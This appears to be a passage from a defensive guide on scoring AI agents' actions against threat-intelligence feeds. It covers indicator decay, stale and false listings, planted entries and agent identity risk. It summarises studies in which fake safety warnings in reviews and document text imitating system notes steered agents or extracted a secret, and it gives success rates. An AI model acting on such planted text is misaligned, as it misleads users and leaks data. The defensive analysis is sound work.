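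An operator should recalculate the published settings before using them. For an IP address with a base score of 80 and a lifetime of seven days, Iklody and colleagues want the score to halve after 48 hours and set the decay speed to 0.55. At that speed, the score after 48 hours is still about 72. Halving it would take a speed of about 1.8, so they seem to have confused the speed with its inverse, the exponent in the formula. Halving the score that early also contradicts their own argument, because the score would then fall fastest at the start.

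Mokaddem, Wagener and colleagues (2019), in *Taxonomy driven indicator scoring in MISP threat intelligence platforms*, repeated the mistake when they fitted the formula to data on 583,783 phishing links. They chose a lifetime of five days and wanted the score to halve after three. Their decay speed of 1.3 would leave only about a third of the score after three days. A speed of about 0.74 would leave half.

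Mokaddem and colleagues also simulated the removal of expired links over two months. Nearly 60% of the removals were correct, but 40% came too early, perhaps partly because they had deliberately left out long-lived links when they chose the lifetime. For an agent, each early removal could turn a match into a miss, so an operator should run a similar simulation on its own feed before letting the software delete anything.

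The score is not a probability, although both can run from 0 to 100. The base score depends on labels that people attach to an entry. In an example from MISP's *Decaying of Indicators* (2019), a source marked "completely reliable" contributes 100 and a highly convincing phishing message contributes 75, which gives a base score of 87.5 with equal weights. How convincing a message is, however, is weak evidence of whether its link is still malicious. The formula also does not account for the base rate, so a fall in the score from 80 to 40 does not mean that a match is half as likely to be true.

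To get a probability, the operator can group reviewed matches by age and count how many in each group were malicious. If 6 of 120 matches on entries between one and two weeks old were malicious, the estimate for that group is 5%. Old entries can then get their own point value in the logarithmic system described earlier. For example, a match on an old entry is worth 2.7 points instead of 3.7.

### Fixed expiry, decay and renewal

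The table compares three ways of handling the entry with a base of 80, a lifetime of 30 days and a speed of 1. On day 20, somebody confirms that the destination is still malicious.

| Day | Fixed expiry after 30 days | Decay without renewal | Decay with renewal |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10 | 80 | 53 | 53 |
| 25 | 80 | 13 | 67 |
| 35 | Removed | 0 | 40 |
| 50 | Removed | 0 | 0 |

Fixed expiry is the easiest method to explain and test. Datadog uses a version of it, keeping vendors' entries for 24 hours and fetching them again at least once a day. An entry therefore stays in use as long as the vendor keeps supplying it, which leaves the vendor to decide when it is stale.

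If the software only checks whether the score is above a threshold, decay has the same effect on any one entry as a fixed expiry. With a threshold of 30, the entry in the table stops counting after 18.75 days. Unlike a single expiry for all entries, though, decay lets better-supported entries last longer. An entry with a base of 50 would stop counting after 12 days. Decay is more useful when the response varies with the score, so that the same old entry can stop an upload but not a page view.

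Renewing an entry keeps it from being deleted while the attack continues. In MISP, each new sighting returns the score to its base. Intrusion-detection software can report its own matches to the platform automatically, so the operator has to be strict about what counts as a sighting. Suppose a bakery takes over a listed address and an agent visits its site every day. If each match counted as a sighting, these visits would keep resetting the score to 80. Only new evidence of malicious use should renew an entry, and a second feed's copy of the entry is not new evidence.

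A failed visit is weak evidence that an attack has ended. In Lee and colleagues' data, 3.2% of the phishing links worked again after three failed visits in a row, so the operator should not remove an entry the first time its page fails to load.

As a rule of thumb, Netresec suggests keeping IP addresses for a couple of weeks after the last sighting and domains a little longer. Domains that malware generates by algorithm typically last only a day. If a feed gives no last sighting, the operator can count from the day it first received the entry, but it will then keep some entries too long because they were already old when they arrived.

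### Cached results, long tasks and saved links

An agent can act on an outdated lookup even when the operator's feed is current. Suppose it first visits supplier-quotes.example at 09:00, before any feed lists the site, and the software stores the result, "no match," for the rest of the task. The feed adds the domain at 09:40. When the agent uploads the manager's order history to the site at 11:00, the software still uses the 09:00 result.

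The simplest remedy is to discard all cached "no match" results when a new copy of the feed arrives. Lookups in a local copy are so fast that the software does not need to cache results at all. With live queries, it could reuse a cached result for page views but query again before the agent uploads data, makes a payment or runs a downloaded program.

Stored IP addresses need even more care. A DNS answer includes a time limit for reusing it, and this limit was under five minutes for half of the phishing sites in Lee and colleagues' study. An attacker can therefore move a site to a new address several times during one task, so the software should check the address again each time it opens a new connection.

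During a long task, a feed may list a page after the agent has already read it. The software should then raise the risk scores of the task's remaining actions, as it would after letting a doubtful page through. If the task involves money or private files, the operator could restart it without the suspect page.

Agents also save links in notes, documents and scheduled jobs. The software should check a link when the agent opens it, even if it passed when the agent saved it, because an attacker may have hijacked the site or bought its expired domain since then.

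An agent may also avoid a legitimate site long after the feed has removed its entry. This can happen if the agent writes "real-wholesaler.example is dangerous" in its long-term memory after a temporary listing. The operator should keep feed results in the lookup system, where they have dates and can expire.

### Rechecking past actions

When a feed lists a destination late, the operator can still find out which agents visited it earlier. Security teams already do this for human users. A sample incident report in *TraceScope* (2026), which presents a system for investigating suspicious links, advises blocking the newly found addresses and searching 30 days of web logs for earlier visits.

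In the supplier example, the fake site became active on 28 September at 06:40 and the feed listed it on 30 September at 09:12. The software should search for visits between those times and perhaps a few days earlier, since the first sighting may not have been the first use. For entries without a starting date, a 30-day search may be too short. The first MOVEit addresses appeared 30 days after the disclosure, so a 30-day search on that day would barely have reached back to the disclosure, and later listings would have needed a longer search.

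The response depends on what the agent did at the destination:

- If it only read a page, check the later actions in the same task for signs of prompt injection.
- If it downloaded a file, isolate the file and find out whether anyone opened or copied it.
- If it entered a password or used an access key, replace it.
- If it sent company data, tell the people responsible for the data, since the operator cannot take it back.

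A past match is no more certain than a live one. If a hacked site was clean when the agent visited, the visit was harmless, and an automatic password reset would cause needless trouble. The operator should compare the time of the visit with the dates in the entry before doing anything disruptive.

This search works only if the log links each request to a task and its files. Otherwise, the operator may learn that some agent contacted the fake wholesaler but not which price list came from it.

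### Feed updates and policy updates

A feed update changes what the operator knows about destinations, while a policy update changes how the software uses that knowledge, for example by adding an exception or lowering a threshold. The two often arrive through different channels, so a new rule may take effect slowly even when the feed updates quickly.

The wait between feed downloads adds to the listing delay. If an operator downloads a feed once a day, a new entry takes 12 hours on average to reach the operator's copy, and more than half of the phishing pages in Lee and colleagues' study went offline sooner than that. Elastic's *MISP Integration*, which imports indicators from MISP into Elastic's security software, lets the operator choose how often to fetch them. For phishing, fetching every few minutes makes more sense than once a day, if the supplier allows it and publishes new entries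 that often.

According to Microsoft, a new exception for a wrongly blocked site in Global Secure Access should work within two minutes, although the user may have to clear the browser's cache. A new security profile, which groups rules for particular users, can take 60 to 90 minutes because the service enforces it through access tokens that users already hold. An administrator can speed this up by revoking the users' sessions, which forces them to obtain new tokens.

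Microsoft says changes to web content filtering for Copilot Studio agents typically take effect in less than five minutes. These agents support only the baseline profile, so the longer delay probably does not apply to them. None of these times measures how quickly a new entry in Microsoft's feeds starts to block traffic.

The difference matters when the operator's own staff discover an attack before any feed lists it. To stop agents from visiting the fake wholesaler, the staff have to add a rule, which is a policy update. At a million requests a day, the agents in the running example would make about 62,500 requests in 90 minutes. The operator should therefore set up the profile and an empty block rule in advance, then add a harmless test domain to the rule and time how long it takes to become unreachable.

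## Handling false and planted listings

Besides entries that have gone stale, feeds contain entries that were wrong from the start. A feed may list a hacked company as an attacker or include a harmless address from a malware report, and an attacker may plant a false entry. The evidence on these errors comes from feeds for ordinary networks. The agent experiments described below tested false warnings and labels in the text a model reads, not false matches in feeds.

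### How wrong entries arise

Noroozian, Korczyński and colleagues (2016) write in *Developing Security Reputation Metrics for Hosting Providers* that much of the crime at hosting companies runs on the hacked servers of legitimate customers. If a criminal breaks into the real wholesaler's site and puts a fake bank login in a forgotten folder, a feed is right to list the URL of that page. But if the feed lists all of real-wholesaler.example as a phishing domain, it mislabels the victim as the attacker, and an agent that fetches the price list gets a false match.

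Noroozian and colleagues examined eight feeds with data from 2014 and found microsoft.com and msn.com listed, presumably because hijacked computers contact such sites to test their internet connection. One phishing feed listed banks and URL shorteners. Popular sites were rare in the feeds overall, and about 30% of the popular domains in a sample from one feed were file-sharing services that probably did host malicious files.

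When a feed lists a shared IP address because of one customer, it also wrongly flags the other customers' sites at that address. *Uncovering IP Address Hosting Types Behind Malicious Websites* (2021) found that the overwhelming majority of malicious domains use shared addresses, and that blocklists do not mark which addresses are shared. The damage may be limited, since *The Web is Still Small After More Than a Decade* found that fewer than 10% of the blocklisted addresses it studied hosted more than 100 domains, and describes the harm to neighbouring sites as minimal. However, that count gives every domain the same weight, regardless of how often agents visit it.

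Domain entries have the same problem. *PhreshPhish* (2025), a collection of phishing pages, reports that the most common domains in phishing links often belong to legitimate services where anyone can publish a page, such as Vercel and Blogspot. *Measuring the Effectiveness of Digital Hygiene using Historical DNS Data* (2021) examines a DNS filter's list of over 300,000 domains, most of them from open feeds, and describes the majority as benign.

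Other errors arise when somebody extracts indicators from a malware report. A sandbox report lists thousands of files, settings and connections, and most of them are ordinary activity of the operating system. Vasan and colleagues ran malware in a sandbox and had two analysts label the true indicators in each report. They then compared two simple rules with three language models on 45 reports, which contained 1,472 true indicators:

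| Method | True indicators found | False indicators | Share of output that is right | Share of true indicators found |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Take every recorded value | 1,472 | 15,019 | 9% | 100% |
| Take values that the malware created or changed | 1,472 | 2,115 | 41% | 100% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 365 | 105 | 78% | 25% |
| GPT-5.5 | 363 | 145 | 71% | 25% |
| GLM 5.2 | 461 | 451 | 51% | 31% |

The models made far fewer false claims than the rules but missed about 70% or more of the true indicators. They tended to report values that looked malicious and overlook those that looked ordinary. The figures combine files, registry keys, network values and mutexes (markers that programs use to avoid running twice), so they don't give a separate error rate for domains or IP addresses.

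The rules resemble standard extraction tools, and 15 of the 18 practitioners Vasan and colleagues surveyed use scripts to process their logs. Only three use language models. Thirteen also analyse logs by hand, which should remove some errors before a feed publishes them.

A victim's own addresses can also get into a report. Vasan and colleagues added 92 identifying details of an invented victim to four incident reports and asked the three models to remove them while keeping the reports useful. The models each missed between 3 and 10 details, including the same three internal network addresses. Many companies use the same private address ranges, so a listed address such as 10.0.0.5 could match a harmless server inside any of them. An operator's import script should discard private addresses.

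### Why a listing is hard to verify

If a listed page shows an error message or harmless content when opened, that does not prove the entry is wrong. Attackers use cloaking to show different content to different visitors. *PhreshPhish* reports that some malicious domains redirect crawlers to an unrelated page, and that others load content in ways a simple crawler cannot capture.

*TraceScope* reports a two-week trial in which an organisation's email analysts submitted 111 suspicious links. Forty were offline. Of the 71 live pages, 18 returned errors or timed out when a standard automated browser opened them, although they worked for people.

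However, harmless sites also block crawlers, so a block is not evidence of phishing. The detection rates in the paper imply that 12 of the 18 pages that blocked the crawler were phishing (67%), compared with 34 of the 53 that it could open (64%).

*TraceScope* argues that many pages that researchers count as dead are live but hidden from crawlers (cloaked). It cites a finding that standard crawlers could not open 61.1% of 15.7 million phishing links. The figure comes from a crawl between July 2021 and July 2023, reported by Ji, Lee and colleagues (2024) in *Evaluating the Effectiveness and Robustness of Visual Similarity-based Phishing Detection Models*. But Ji and colleagues attribute the failures to server shutdowns and network errors, such as failed DNS lookups, not to cloaking. Their figure shows how often listed pages are unreachable, and the evidence for cloaking is the 18 pages in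 *TraceScope*'s own small trial.

Pages that do open may have changed since they were reported. In a separate test, *TraceScope* used 1,000 reachable links, including 531 that PhishTank had marked as verified phishing pages that were still online. The original content was gone or replaced on 236 of the 1,000. Nearly all of these must have been phishing links, because only two harmless links dropped out of the test for any reason. About 44% of the reachable PhishTank entries therefore no longer showed what the feed had reported. *Evaluating the effectiveness of Phishing Reports on Twitter* (2021) found that 24.2% of a sample of PhishTank links were already inactive when first listed, which was too late to verify them.

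A reviewer who finds an error page should record the match as unclear. Counting the match as false would make a good feed look bad and could lead the operator to exempt a live phishing site.

An automated investigation can help determine whether a match is malicious, but it is not conclusive. In the trial, *TraceScope*'s agents, which click through a page as a person would, recognised 30 of the 46 phishing pages and wrongly flagged 2 of the 25 harmless ones. At these rates, for the 105 daily matches in the running example, a flag would raise the probability that a match is malicious from 4.8% to about 29%, and a clean result would lower it to about 2%. At the median cost of $0.24 per link, the checks would cost roughly $25 a day, or more if many pages were hard to inspect. The checks take too long to run before every page view, but the operator could use them to decide which entries to exempt.

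### What a false match does to an agent's task

This sequence is inferred from how agents and reviewers work, not from measurements. Suppose a feed wrongly lists real-wholesaler.example and the purchasing manager's agent tries to open the site's price list. The enforcement point blocks the request with an error that looks like a temporary fault, so the agent retries three times, and the log then contains four entries for one false match.

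It then looks for the prices elsewhere and finds a reseller's page from last year, or it leaves the wholesaler out. The manager receives a comparison of four suppliers and has no reason to suspect the cheapest one is missing. If the wholesaler charges 42 cents a box and the next supplier charges 47, an order of 100,000 boxes costs $5,000 more than necessary. A person who saw a browser warning would at least know something had gone wrong.

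The operator can limit this damage with a clear reply. The reply should say that a policy blocked the site and instruct the agent not to retry and to mark the supplier as unchecked in its answer. It should not call the supplier dangerous, because the agent may repeat that claim to the manager.

If the software asks a person instead, false matches gradually make approval a habit. In the running example, a reviewer who approved everything without reading would be right about 20 times out of 21. Repeated requests for the same site strengthen the habit, so the software should group them into one question per task.

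False matches also tend to come from a few entries. If 60 of the 100 daily false matches in the running example came from the wholesaler's entry, correcting it would leave 5 true matches and 40 false ones. The probability that a match is malicious would rise from 4.8% to 11%. The operator should therefore rank entries by how many tasks they interrupt and review the top ones first.

### Remedies and what they cost

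One remedy is to act only when independent feeds agree. This removes errors that a single supplier makes, but it also discards many correct entries. *BotScan* (2026) describes a method for finding the control servers of botnets made up of hijacked household devices, and compares 382 live servers with three sources. One of them, VirusTotal, collects the verdicts of many security vendors, and *BotScan* counts a server as listed there if at least one vendor flagged it. The paper does not give the overlap between the sources, but its totals set limits:

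| Requirement for a match | Servers matched, of 382 |
|---|---|
| VirusTotal | 300 (79%) |
| URLhaus | 267 (70%) |
| IBM X-Force | 80 (21%) |
| VirusTotal and URLhaus | 185 to 267 (48% to 70%) |
| All three | At most 80 (21%) |

The loss can be greater for other kinds of entries. In Noroozian and colleagues' data, 93% of domain and IP address pairs appeared in only one feed, partly because the feeds covered different kinds of abuse.

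An operator should therefore require feeds to agree only where wrongly blocking an action would do a lot of harm compared with the harm the action itself might do. In the running example, a single match justifies blocking the upload of a customer file, so requiring a match in a second feed would let through attacks that the operator has good reason to stop.

Matching the full URL instead of the host protects the wholesaler's price list when only a page in another folder is malicious. But the attacker can escape the match by moving that page, and the check needs an enforcement point that can read full URLs. A sensible compromise is to decide how much to match by who owns the domain. If an attacker registered the domain, the software should match every page. If it belongs to a hacked business or a service such as Google Forms, where *TraceScope* found a fake benefit programme that asked for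 social security numbers, the software should match the URL. Customers of Vercel and Blogspot have their own subdomains, so the software can match the subdomain without affecting other customers.

The operator can give less weight to shared IP addresses. The classifier in *Uncovering IP Address Hosting Types Behind Malicious Websites* separated shared from dedicated addresses with about 94% precision. An operator without such a tool could count how many unrelated domains its own agents have reached at an address.

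Exceptions are the quickest remedy for a single wrong entry, but they can hide a later attack. In Microsoft's instructions, an administrator gives an exception a name, description, priority, status and list of domains. The steps include no end date, so the operator needs its own reminder to remove the exception. A system that the operator builds itself can store narrower exceptions:

```json
{
  "indicator_id": "indicator--7c2e91d4-0b6f-4a38-9e15-d3f8a1b04c67",
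  "url_prefix": "https://real-wholesaler.example/prices/",
  "allowed_actions": ["read_page"],
  "task": "packaging-comparison",
  "expires": "2026-10-14T09:00:00Z",
  "reason": "Fake login was in another folder; owner has removed it"
}
```

This exception lets the agent read prices for one task during one week. It does not allow uploads. It covers only one particular indicator, so a new report about the same site would still cause a match. The drawback is that somebody has to renew the exception if the feed has not corrected its entry by the end of the week.

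The operator should also report the error to the feed's supplier, with the URL, the time of the check and a screenshot. A correction helps every customer of the feed, but it may not reach other feeds that copied the entry, so the operator should check those separately. The supplier will learn from the report which sites the agents use. Suppliers have to be sceptical of correction requests, because an attacker can just as easily complain about a correct entry.

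### Entries that somebody plants

An attacker could use a feed to block a competitor. *Challenges and Opportunities of Blockchain for Cyber Threat Intelligence Sharing* (2022) suggests that somebody could write plausible intelligence that makes the recipients' software flag legitimate activity. It also describes flooding a sharing platform with fake reports so that a real warning gets lost. Both scenarios are theoretical.

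A dishonest supplier who got the real wholesaler listed would remove it from the comparisons of every agent that relies on the feed. The same method could disable a defence if the feed listed its own update server or a site that publishes security fixes, because a strict blocking rule would then cut the operator off from it. Operators should keep a short list of such services and require a person to confirm any new match on them.

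The attacker may not have to write a report. Some vendors shared indicators from Galloway and colleagues' harmless programs, so an attacker could submit a program that contacts a rival's site and hope that a vendor extracts the domain. But the researchers used their own unknown domains, so their experiment does not show that vendors would accept a well-known business's domain as an indicator.

Researchers have studied poisoned threat intelligence for years. The 2023 survey *NLP-Based Techniques for Cyber Threat Intelligence* cites a poisoning attack on VirusTotal that McAfee researchers described. It also reports an experiment in which GPT-2, an early language model, wrote fake threat reports that contaminated a system that extracts knowledge from such reports.

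A false report that something is safe may help an attacker more than a false report that it is dangerous. *Preventing Poisoning Attacks on AI based Threat Intelligence Systems* (2018) considers an attacker who publishes a claim that a real vulnerability does not exist, and proposes checking such claims with a reputation engine.

*AuthRank* (2025) tests a similar attack on a language model that answers questions from a collection of threat reports. The attacker publishes a blog post calling a new domain benign, then uses the domain to spread malware. No other document mentioned the domain, so the post alone misled the system. When the researchers added a score for each source's credibility, the system answered that it had little authoritative information. This was a single demonstration, so it does not show how often the defence would work.

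Software that checks agents' actions against these feeds should treat "benign" entries with more suspicion than malicious ones, because the company could lose its customer files if a dangerous site is listed as benign. Wrongly listing a site as malicious usually means the agent loses a supplier. The software should lower a risk score only for an exception the operator has approved, never because an outside report lists a site as safe.

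### Fake safety warnings on web pages

An attacker who cannot get a rival listed in a threat feed can instead plant a false accusation in text the agent will read. *Voluntary Servitude* (Zendel, Levy and colleagues, 2026) tested whether invented safety warnings in customer reviews could steer agents that choose travel services. The reviews described a hazard at the legitimate companies and recommended a fictitious competitor. Unlike an ordinary prompt injection, they contained no instructions to the model.

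The fake warnings led the models to choose the competitor in 60.4% of cases, compared with 66.0% for ordinary prompt injections. Complaints about unethical conduct succeeded in only 8.2%, so the warnings worked because they claimed danger. In most successful cases, the model ruled out the legitimate companies as unsafe. Two commercial prompt-injection detectors let through 100% and 78% of the fake warnings, but only 54% and 16% of the injections.

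In the main tests, the attacker wrote a quarter of the reviews. In a smaller test, only four fake reviews among 120 still succeeded 74% of the time.

Zendel and colleagues then showed a page with such reviews to four browser agents, 20 times per attack:

| Browser agent | Fake warning succeeded | Prompt injection succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| Edge with Copilot | 100% | 20% |
| Brave's assistant | 100% | 100% |
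| Comet | 60% | 0% |
| OpenAI's Codex browser | 20% | 0% |

As a defence, the researchers also tested adding an instruction not to reject a company on safety grounds without independent confirmation. Across three models, it reduced the attack's success rate from 68.4% to 3.6%. The models still mentioned the hazard in nearly every answer but rarely acted on it. However, the attacker in this test did not adapt, and could have spread the claim over more accounts and sites. The instruction also makes an agent wait for confirmation when a single honest customer reports a real danger.

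These warnings were reviews, not imitations of a feed's verdict, and the agents only made recommendations. But the results suggest that an agent would probably drop the real wholesaler if the operator's software returned a warning that it was dangerous, even if the match were false. This is another reason to send a neutral reply.

If planted reviews falsely warn the agent away from the real wholesaler and send it to supplier-quotes.example, a feed lookup still stops the visit, provided the feed lists that domain.

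### Keeping verdicts separate from page text

An operator's software might write "Threat lookup: no match" into the model's prompt and then let the model decide whether to proceed. A malicious page can contain the same words. Both appear as text in the same prompt, so the model may not be able to distinguish the software's result from the page's imitation.

Zhu (2026), in *Document-Authored Control-Signal Impersonation*, tested a closely related weakness. The attacker's documents contained labels that imitated system notes, such as a claim that the source was verified or that exact quotation was allowed. The models had instructions not to reveal a dummy password. When the task pressed for an exact copy of the text, DeepSeek V4 Pro revealed the password in 0.5% of answers without the labels and 28% with them. GPT-5.5 revealed it in only about 1% of cases in a comparison of attacks. The test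 involved secrets rather than feed verdicts, but a false "no match" would exploit the same confusion between document text and system notes.

The operator can avoid the problem by keeping the model out of the decision. The lookup software sends its record directly to the code at the enforcement point, which calculates the score and allows or blocks the call. The agent receives only the outcome. The record should include an identifier for the tool call, so that the code cannot use an earlier "no match" to approve a later request to another site.

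Page text should not be able to raise a score the way a feed match does, either. If a review says that a feed lists the real wholesaler as a phishing site, the software can look up the domain itself. The review may still be a reason to investigate.

A second language model that judges difficult actions, as in AgentBouncer, may need both the feed's verdict and part of the page. The software should supply them in separate fields, and fixed code should enforce any mandatory block regardless of the model's output. Separate fields make the model less likely to mistake page text for the feed's verdict, but may not prevent it, because the model still processes everything as text.

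The feed entry can contain an attacker's words. In STIX, an indicator's name is free text, and a supplier may have copied it from a malicious file or a social-media post. The software should therefore pass the second model only fixed-format values, such as the threat type, confidence and dates. A human reviewer can see the full entry, shown visibly separate from the page.

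## Scoring known bad actors and malicious tools

Most of the indicators discussed so far describe where an agent's request goes. Others describe a party, which may be an operator's own agent that an attacker has hijacked, an unfamiliar agent that visits a website, or the publisher of a skill. Flagging a destination affects only the scores of requests sent there, but flagging a party affects the scores of everything it does afterwards, so the operator has to decide how much the flag should raise those scores and when it should expire.

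This section draws more of its evidence from agents than earlier sections do. Microsoft's documentation describes risk levels for agents but doesn't include error rates. Researchers have measured how well a website can recognise agents, but not whether it can recognise malicious ones. The most direct evidence on threat intelligence comes from ClawHub, a marketplace for skills, where scans missed several malicious skills.

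### When an attacker hijacks the operator's own agent

Suppose the purchasing manager's company registers its agents with Microsoft Entra. This service manages identities and issues access tokens, the temporary passes that software presents to mailboxes, file stores and other resources. A part of it called Entra ID Protection learns what each agent normally does and flags departures from that pattern. Microsoft lists six detections:

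| Detection | What triggers it |
|---|---|
| Unfamiliar resource access | The agent tries to reach resources it does not usually use |
| Sign-in spike | The agent signs in more often than usual |
| Failed access attempt | The agent tries and fails to reach resources it has no permission for |
| Sign-in by risky user | The agent signs in on behalf of a user whose account may be compromised |
| Confirmed compromised | An administrator confirms that the agent is compromised |
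| Microsoft Entra threat intelligence | Activity fits attack patterns known from Microsoft's own or outside intelligence |

Only the last detection directly compares activity with threat intelligence. Microsoft does not name the sources, so this detection may repeat entries from a feed the operator already uses and should not count as independent evidence.

The detections contribute to a risk level of low, medium or high, Microsoft's estimate of how likely it is that somebody has compromised the agent. In its general guide to risk levels, written mainly for user accounts, Microsoft reserves "high" for when it is highly confident of a compromise. The level does not reflect what the agent is about to do, so an operator still has to combine it with the harm the action could do, as with a feed match.

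Administrators can use an access policy to block agents based on their risk level. Without one, a flagged agent can keep working indefinitely. Entra checks its policies each time an agent requests a token. In Microsoft's template, the administrator selects all agent identities and all resources, sets the condition to high agent risk, and chooses "Block". The policy starts in report-only mode, so the administrator can see its effect before it blocks anything. Microsoft also provides a ready-made policy that blocks high-risk agents, and its *Enable ID Protection and Deploy Risk-Based Conditional Access for Agents* advises customers to check that this policy is on.

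The policy does not cover every way an agent gets access. Microsoft's *Conditional Access for agent identities* distinguishes several cases:

| How the agent gets access | Whose token it is | What a policy can do |
|---|---|---|
| On behalf of a signed-in user | The user's | Block or ask for further proof of identity, based on signals such as the user's risk |
| With its own identity | The agent's | Block, based on the agent's risk |
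| With its own user account, which may include a mailbox | That account's | Block, but only through a separate policy for such accounts |
| With an API key, a fixed secret that some services accept | Entra issues no token | Nothing |

The policy against high-risk agents does not apply when the supplier-comparison agent reads files on the manager's behalf, so the company would also need a policy for the manager's account. When an agent uses its own identity, blocking is the only option, because the agent cannot answer a request for further proof as a person could.

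### Why the block may come too late

All six detections run offline, meaning after the agent has signed in. According to Microsoft's general guide, offline detections can take up to 48 hours to appear in reports. An agent sending one email a minute could send 2,880 in that time. An agent may also keep using its current token until it has to request a new one.

Attackers can work much faster than that. Unit 42, Palo Alto Networks' security research team, described an intrusion in which agents did weeks of work in less than 10 hours. Help Net Security's *Threat actors are giving AI agents a bigger role in cyberattacks* (2026) reports that Google investigated a campaign that took less than six hours to plan, build and carry out, and that compromised thousands of credentials. These attackers ran their own agents, but a hijacked agent could presumably work at a similar speed. Microsoft presents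 its policy as a way to block agents before they complete an attack, which seems optimistic for attacks this fast.

The anomaly detections may also miss harmful actions caused by prompt injection. Suppose a planted review tells the agent to email the manager's price list to an attacker. The agent opens the mailbox it uses every day, with its usual token and no extra sign-ins, so there is nothing obvious to trigger a detection. A lookup of the recipient's domain at the tool interface is more likely to catch this, because it checks the action itself before the email is sent.

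The operator can connect the two systems. If its own lookup shows that an agent has sent data to a listed address, an administrator can investigate and select "Confirm compromise" in the report of risky agents. This sets the agent's risk level to high and triggers any policy that blocks at that level. To clear a risk, the administrator can select "Confirm safe", which tells the software to avoid flagging similar activity, or "Dismiss risk", which lets it keep flagging such activity. After a security exercise in which staff attack their own agent, the administrator should dismiss the risk so that a real attack of the same kind still raises an alarm.

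### How long a hijacked agent stays suspect

The right duration depends on what the attacker controls. Planted instructions affect an agent as long as they remain in the text it works from, and a stolen key stays dangerous until somebody replaces it.

When an agent reads a page that may contain planted instructions, the operator should mark the task to record that risk. In the running example, a page that matches a feed has a 4.8% chance of being malicious, and the operator lets the agent read it without credentials. Suppose one in ten malicious pages contains instructions that the agent follows. After reading the page, the agent has a 0.48% chance of following an attacker's instructions. At that probability and with the earlier invented costs, the operator should still allow page views and quote forms but ask a person before the agent uploads a customer file. The upload needs this check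 even if the file's destination matches no feed, because the agent itself may be following an attacker's instructions.

The mark can end with the task if the next task starts in a fresh session. If the agent wrote notes to its long-term memory after reading the page, the operator should delete or check those notes first. Otherwise, the planted instructions could return in a later task without triggering a new match.

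When an agent's key is stolen, the scoring system must mark the agent's identity as risky. Unlike the score of an IP address, this mark should not fade with time, because an attacker who holds the key can wait for it to expire. Microsoft follows this logic for user accounts, where low risk expires after six months but medium and high risk last until somebody fixes or dismisses the problem. It does not say whether the same periods apply to agents. It keeps agents' risk detections for up to 90 days, so an operator who expects a longer investigation should export them.

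If the agent is risky only because it signed in for a risky user, its score can return to normal once someone has secured the user's account and checked what the agent did in the meantime.

### When an unknown agent visits a website

The real wholesaler faces a different problem when an unknown agent opens its web shop. The shop can look up the agent's address, read the name it declares, check for a signature, and record its browser properties and behaviour.

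| Signal | What it identifies | How an attacker can escape it | How long a bad mark should last |
|---|---|---|---|
| Source address | A server, a network or a household | Use another address | Hours, or a day at most for a shared address |
| Declared name | Whatever the visitor claims to be | Send a different name | This visit |
| Signed request | The holder of a secret key | Stop signing or register a new key | Until the key's owner has dealt with the abuse |
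| Browser fingerprint | A type of browser and machine | Change the reported settings | This visit |
| Behaviour fingerprint | The software that operates the page | Imitate a person's typing and pointer movements | This visit |

The durations are suggestions based on how easily each signal changes, since none of the studies here tested them.

Feeds contain many source addresses, but an address is a poor guide to who sent an agent. *FP-Agent* (Wang, Shafiq and Vekaria, 2026) covers seven agents that operate a web browser for their users. Two, ChatGPT Agent and Manus, run in the provider's cloud, where many customers' agents may share an address. The other five run on the user's computer, so their requests come from the same address as the user's ordinary browsing.

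Suppose agents make 5,000 visits a day to the wholesaler from one cloud address, and 50 of those visits are attempts to guess passwords. A feed lists the address after someone reports it. Blocking the address would turn away 99 legitimate visits for every malicious one. If the attacker moved to a new address the next day, every later match on the old one would be a false positive. The wholesaler should let visitors from this address read prices and reserve extra checks for logins and orders.

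Attackers also hide behind other people's addresses. In the campaign that Google investigated, the attacker ran agents from a victim's cloud account, so the traffic came from legitimate addresses, and the agents switched between addresses on their own. Feeds may also be late to list an attacker's own servers. Help Net Security's *Attackers breached 10 organizations with an open-source AI pentest framework* (2026) reports that Unit 42 traced intrusion attempts against at least 19 organisations in August and September 2026 to Cairn, a tool that lets a language model choose and run each step of an attack. The article appeared in November, so a website that relied on the two indicators Unit 42 published, both IP addresses, would have had nothing to match during the attacks.

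The declared name is even weaker evidence, because anyone can copy the short text that a browser sends to name its software. Many browsing agents use an ordinary Chromium browser and send the same text as a person's browser would.

A signed request is harder to fake. With Web Bot Auth, an emerging method, the agent's provider signs part of the request with a secret key, and the website checks the signature. The signature shows which provider sent the agent, but not whether the customer behind it means harm. It also gives the wholesaler a more stable identity than a cloud address to attach a record to. But Wang and colleagues name Atlas, Browser Use, Comet and Skyvern as agents that do not use Web Bot Auth, so a missing signature is little reason for suspicion.

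### Recognising agents by how they use a page

Wang and colleagues tested whether a website can recognise agents without their cooperation. They built a site with three tasks: booking a flight, shopping, and reading and writing in a forum. Seven agents each completed about 1,000 runs, and 56 students provided 546 runs for comparison. A script on the site recorded 418 browser features, such as fonts and screen size, and 50 behavioural features, such as the time between keystrokes.

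Every agent's pointer jumped straight to each click, whereas the students' pointers left a continuous path. Several agents pasted text or filled in a field all at once. Others pressed keys only a few milliseconds apart, while the students typed more slowly and much less evenly.

The researchers then trained a classifier to identify whether a person or a particular agent was behind each run. They trained it on 80% of the runs and tested it on the other 20%. They also repeated the test with one task left out of the training data. The table gives F1 scores, where 1 is perfect. F1 combines how often the classifier's labels are right with what share of each kind of run it finds.

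| Features | All tasks in training | Forum left out | Flight booking left out | Shopping left out |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Browser only | 0.82 | Not tested | Not tested | Not tested |
| Behaviour only | 0.999 | 0.80 | 0.63 | 0.74 |
| Both | 1.00 | 0.93 | 0.97 | 0.97 |

The near-perfect scores probably overstate what a web shop would achieve. The researchers ran the local agents on only three computers, while the students used their own, so a classifier with access to browser features could partly learn to recognise the test machines. This may also explain why the combined version did so well on new tasks. The version that used only behaviour, which does not have this problem, did much worse on unfamiliar tasks. The classifier also has no category for unknown agents, and future agents might imitate people better.

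The classifier's score levelled off after about a minute of observing a visitor when it used both kinds of features, and after about three minutes when it used behaviour alone. Most agents finished the tasks within three minutes. The wholesaler could therefore use the result at checkout but not when the first page loads.

Wang and colleagues also tried the free bot protection from Cloudflare, a company that many websites use to filter traffic. With the AI bot controls switched on, Cloudflare fully blocked only Manus, and the other six agents completed the tasks. Manus appears in Cloudflare's directory of verified bots, so the block probably worked because Manus identified itself. Cloudflare also stopped some requests from Anthropic's and Perplexity's servers, but those companies' agents kept working from the researchers' own computers.

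FP-Agent identifies software but not intent. A shop that treated every agent as an attacker would lose customers like the purchasing manager. Suppose agents made 30% of password-guessing visits and 3% of ordinary ones. The likelihood ratio would be 10, which adds one point to the logarithmic score described earlier. That could justify an extra check at login but not refusing to show prices.

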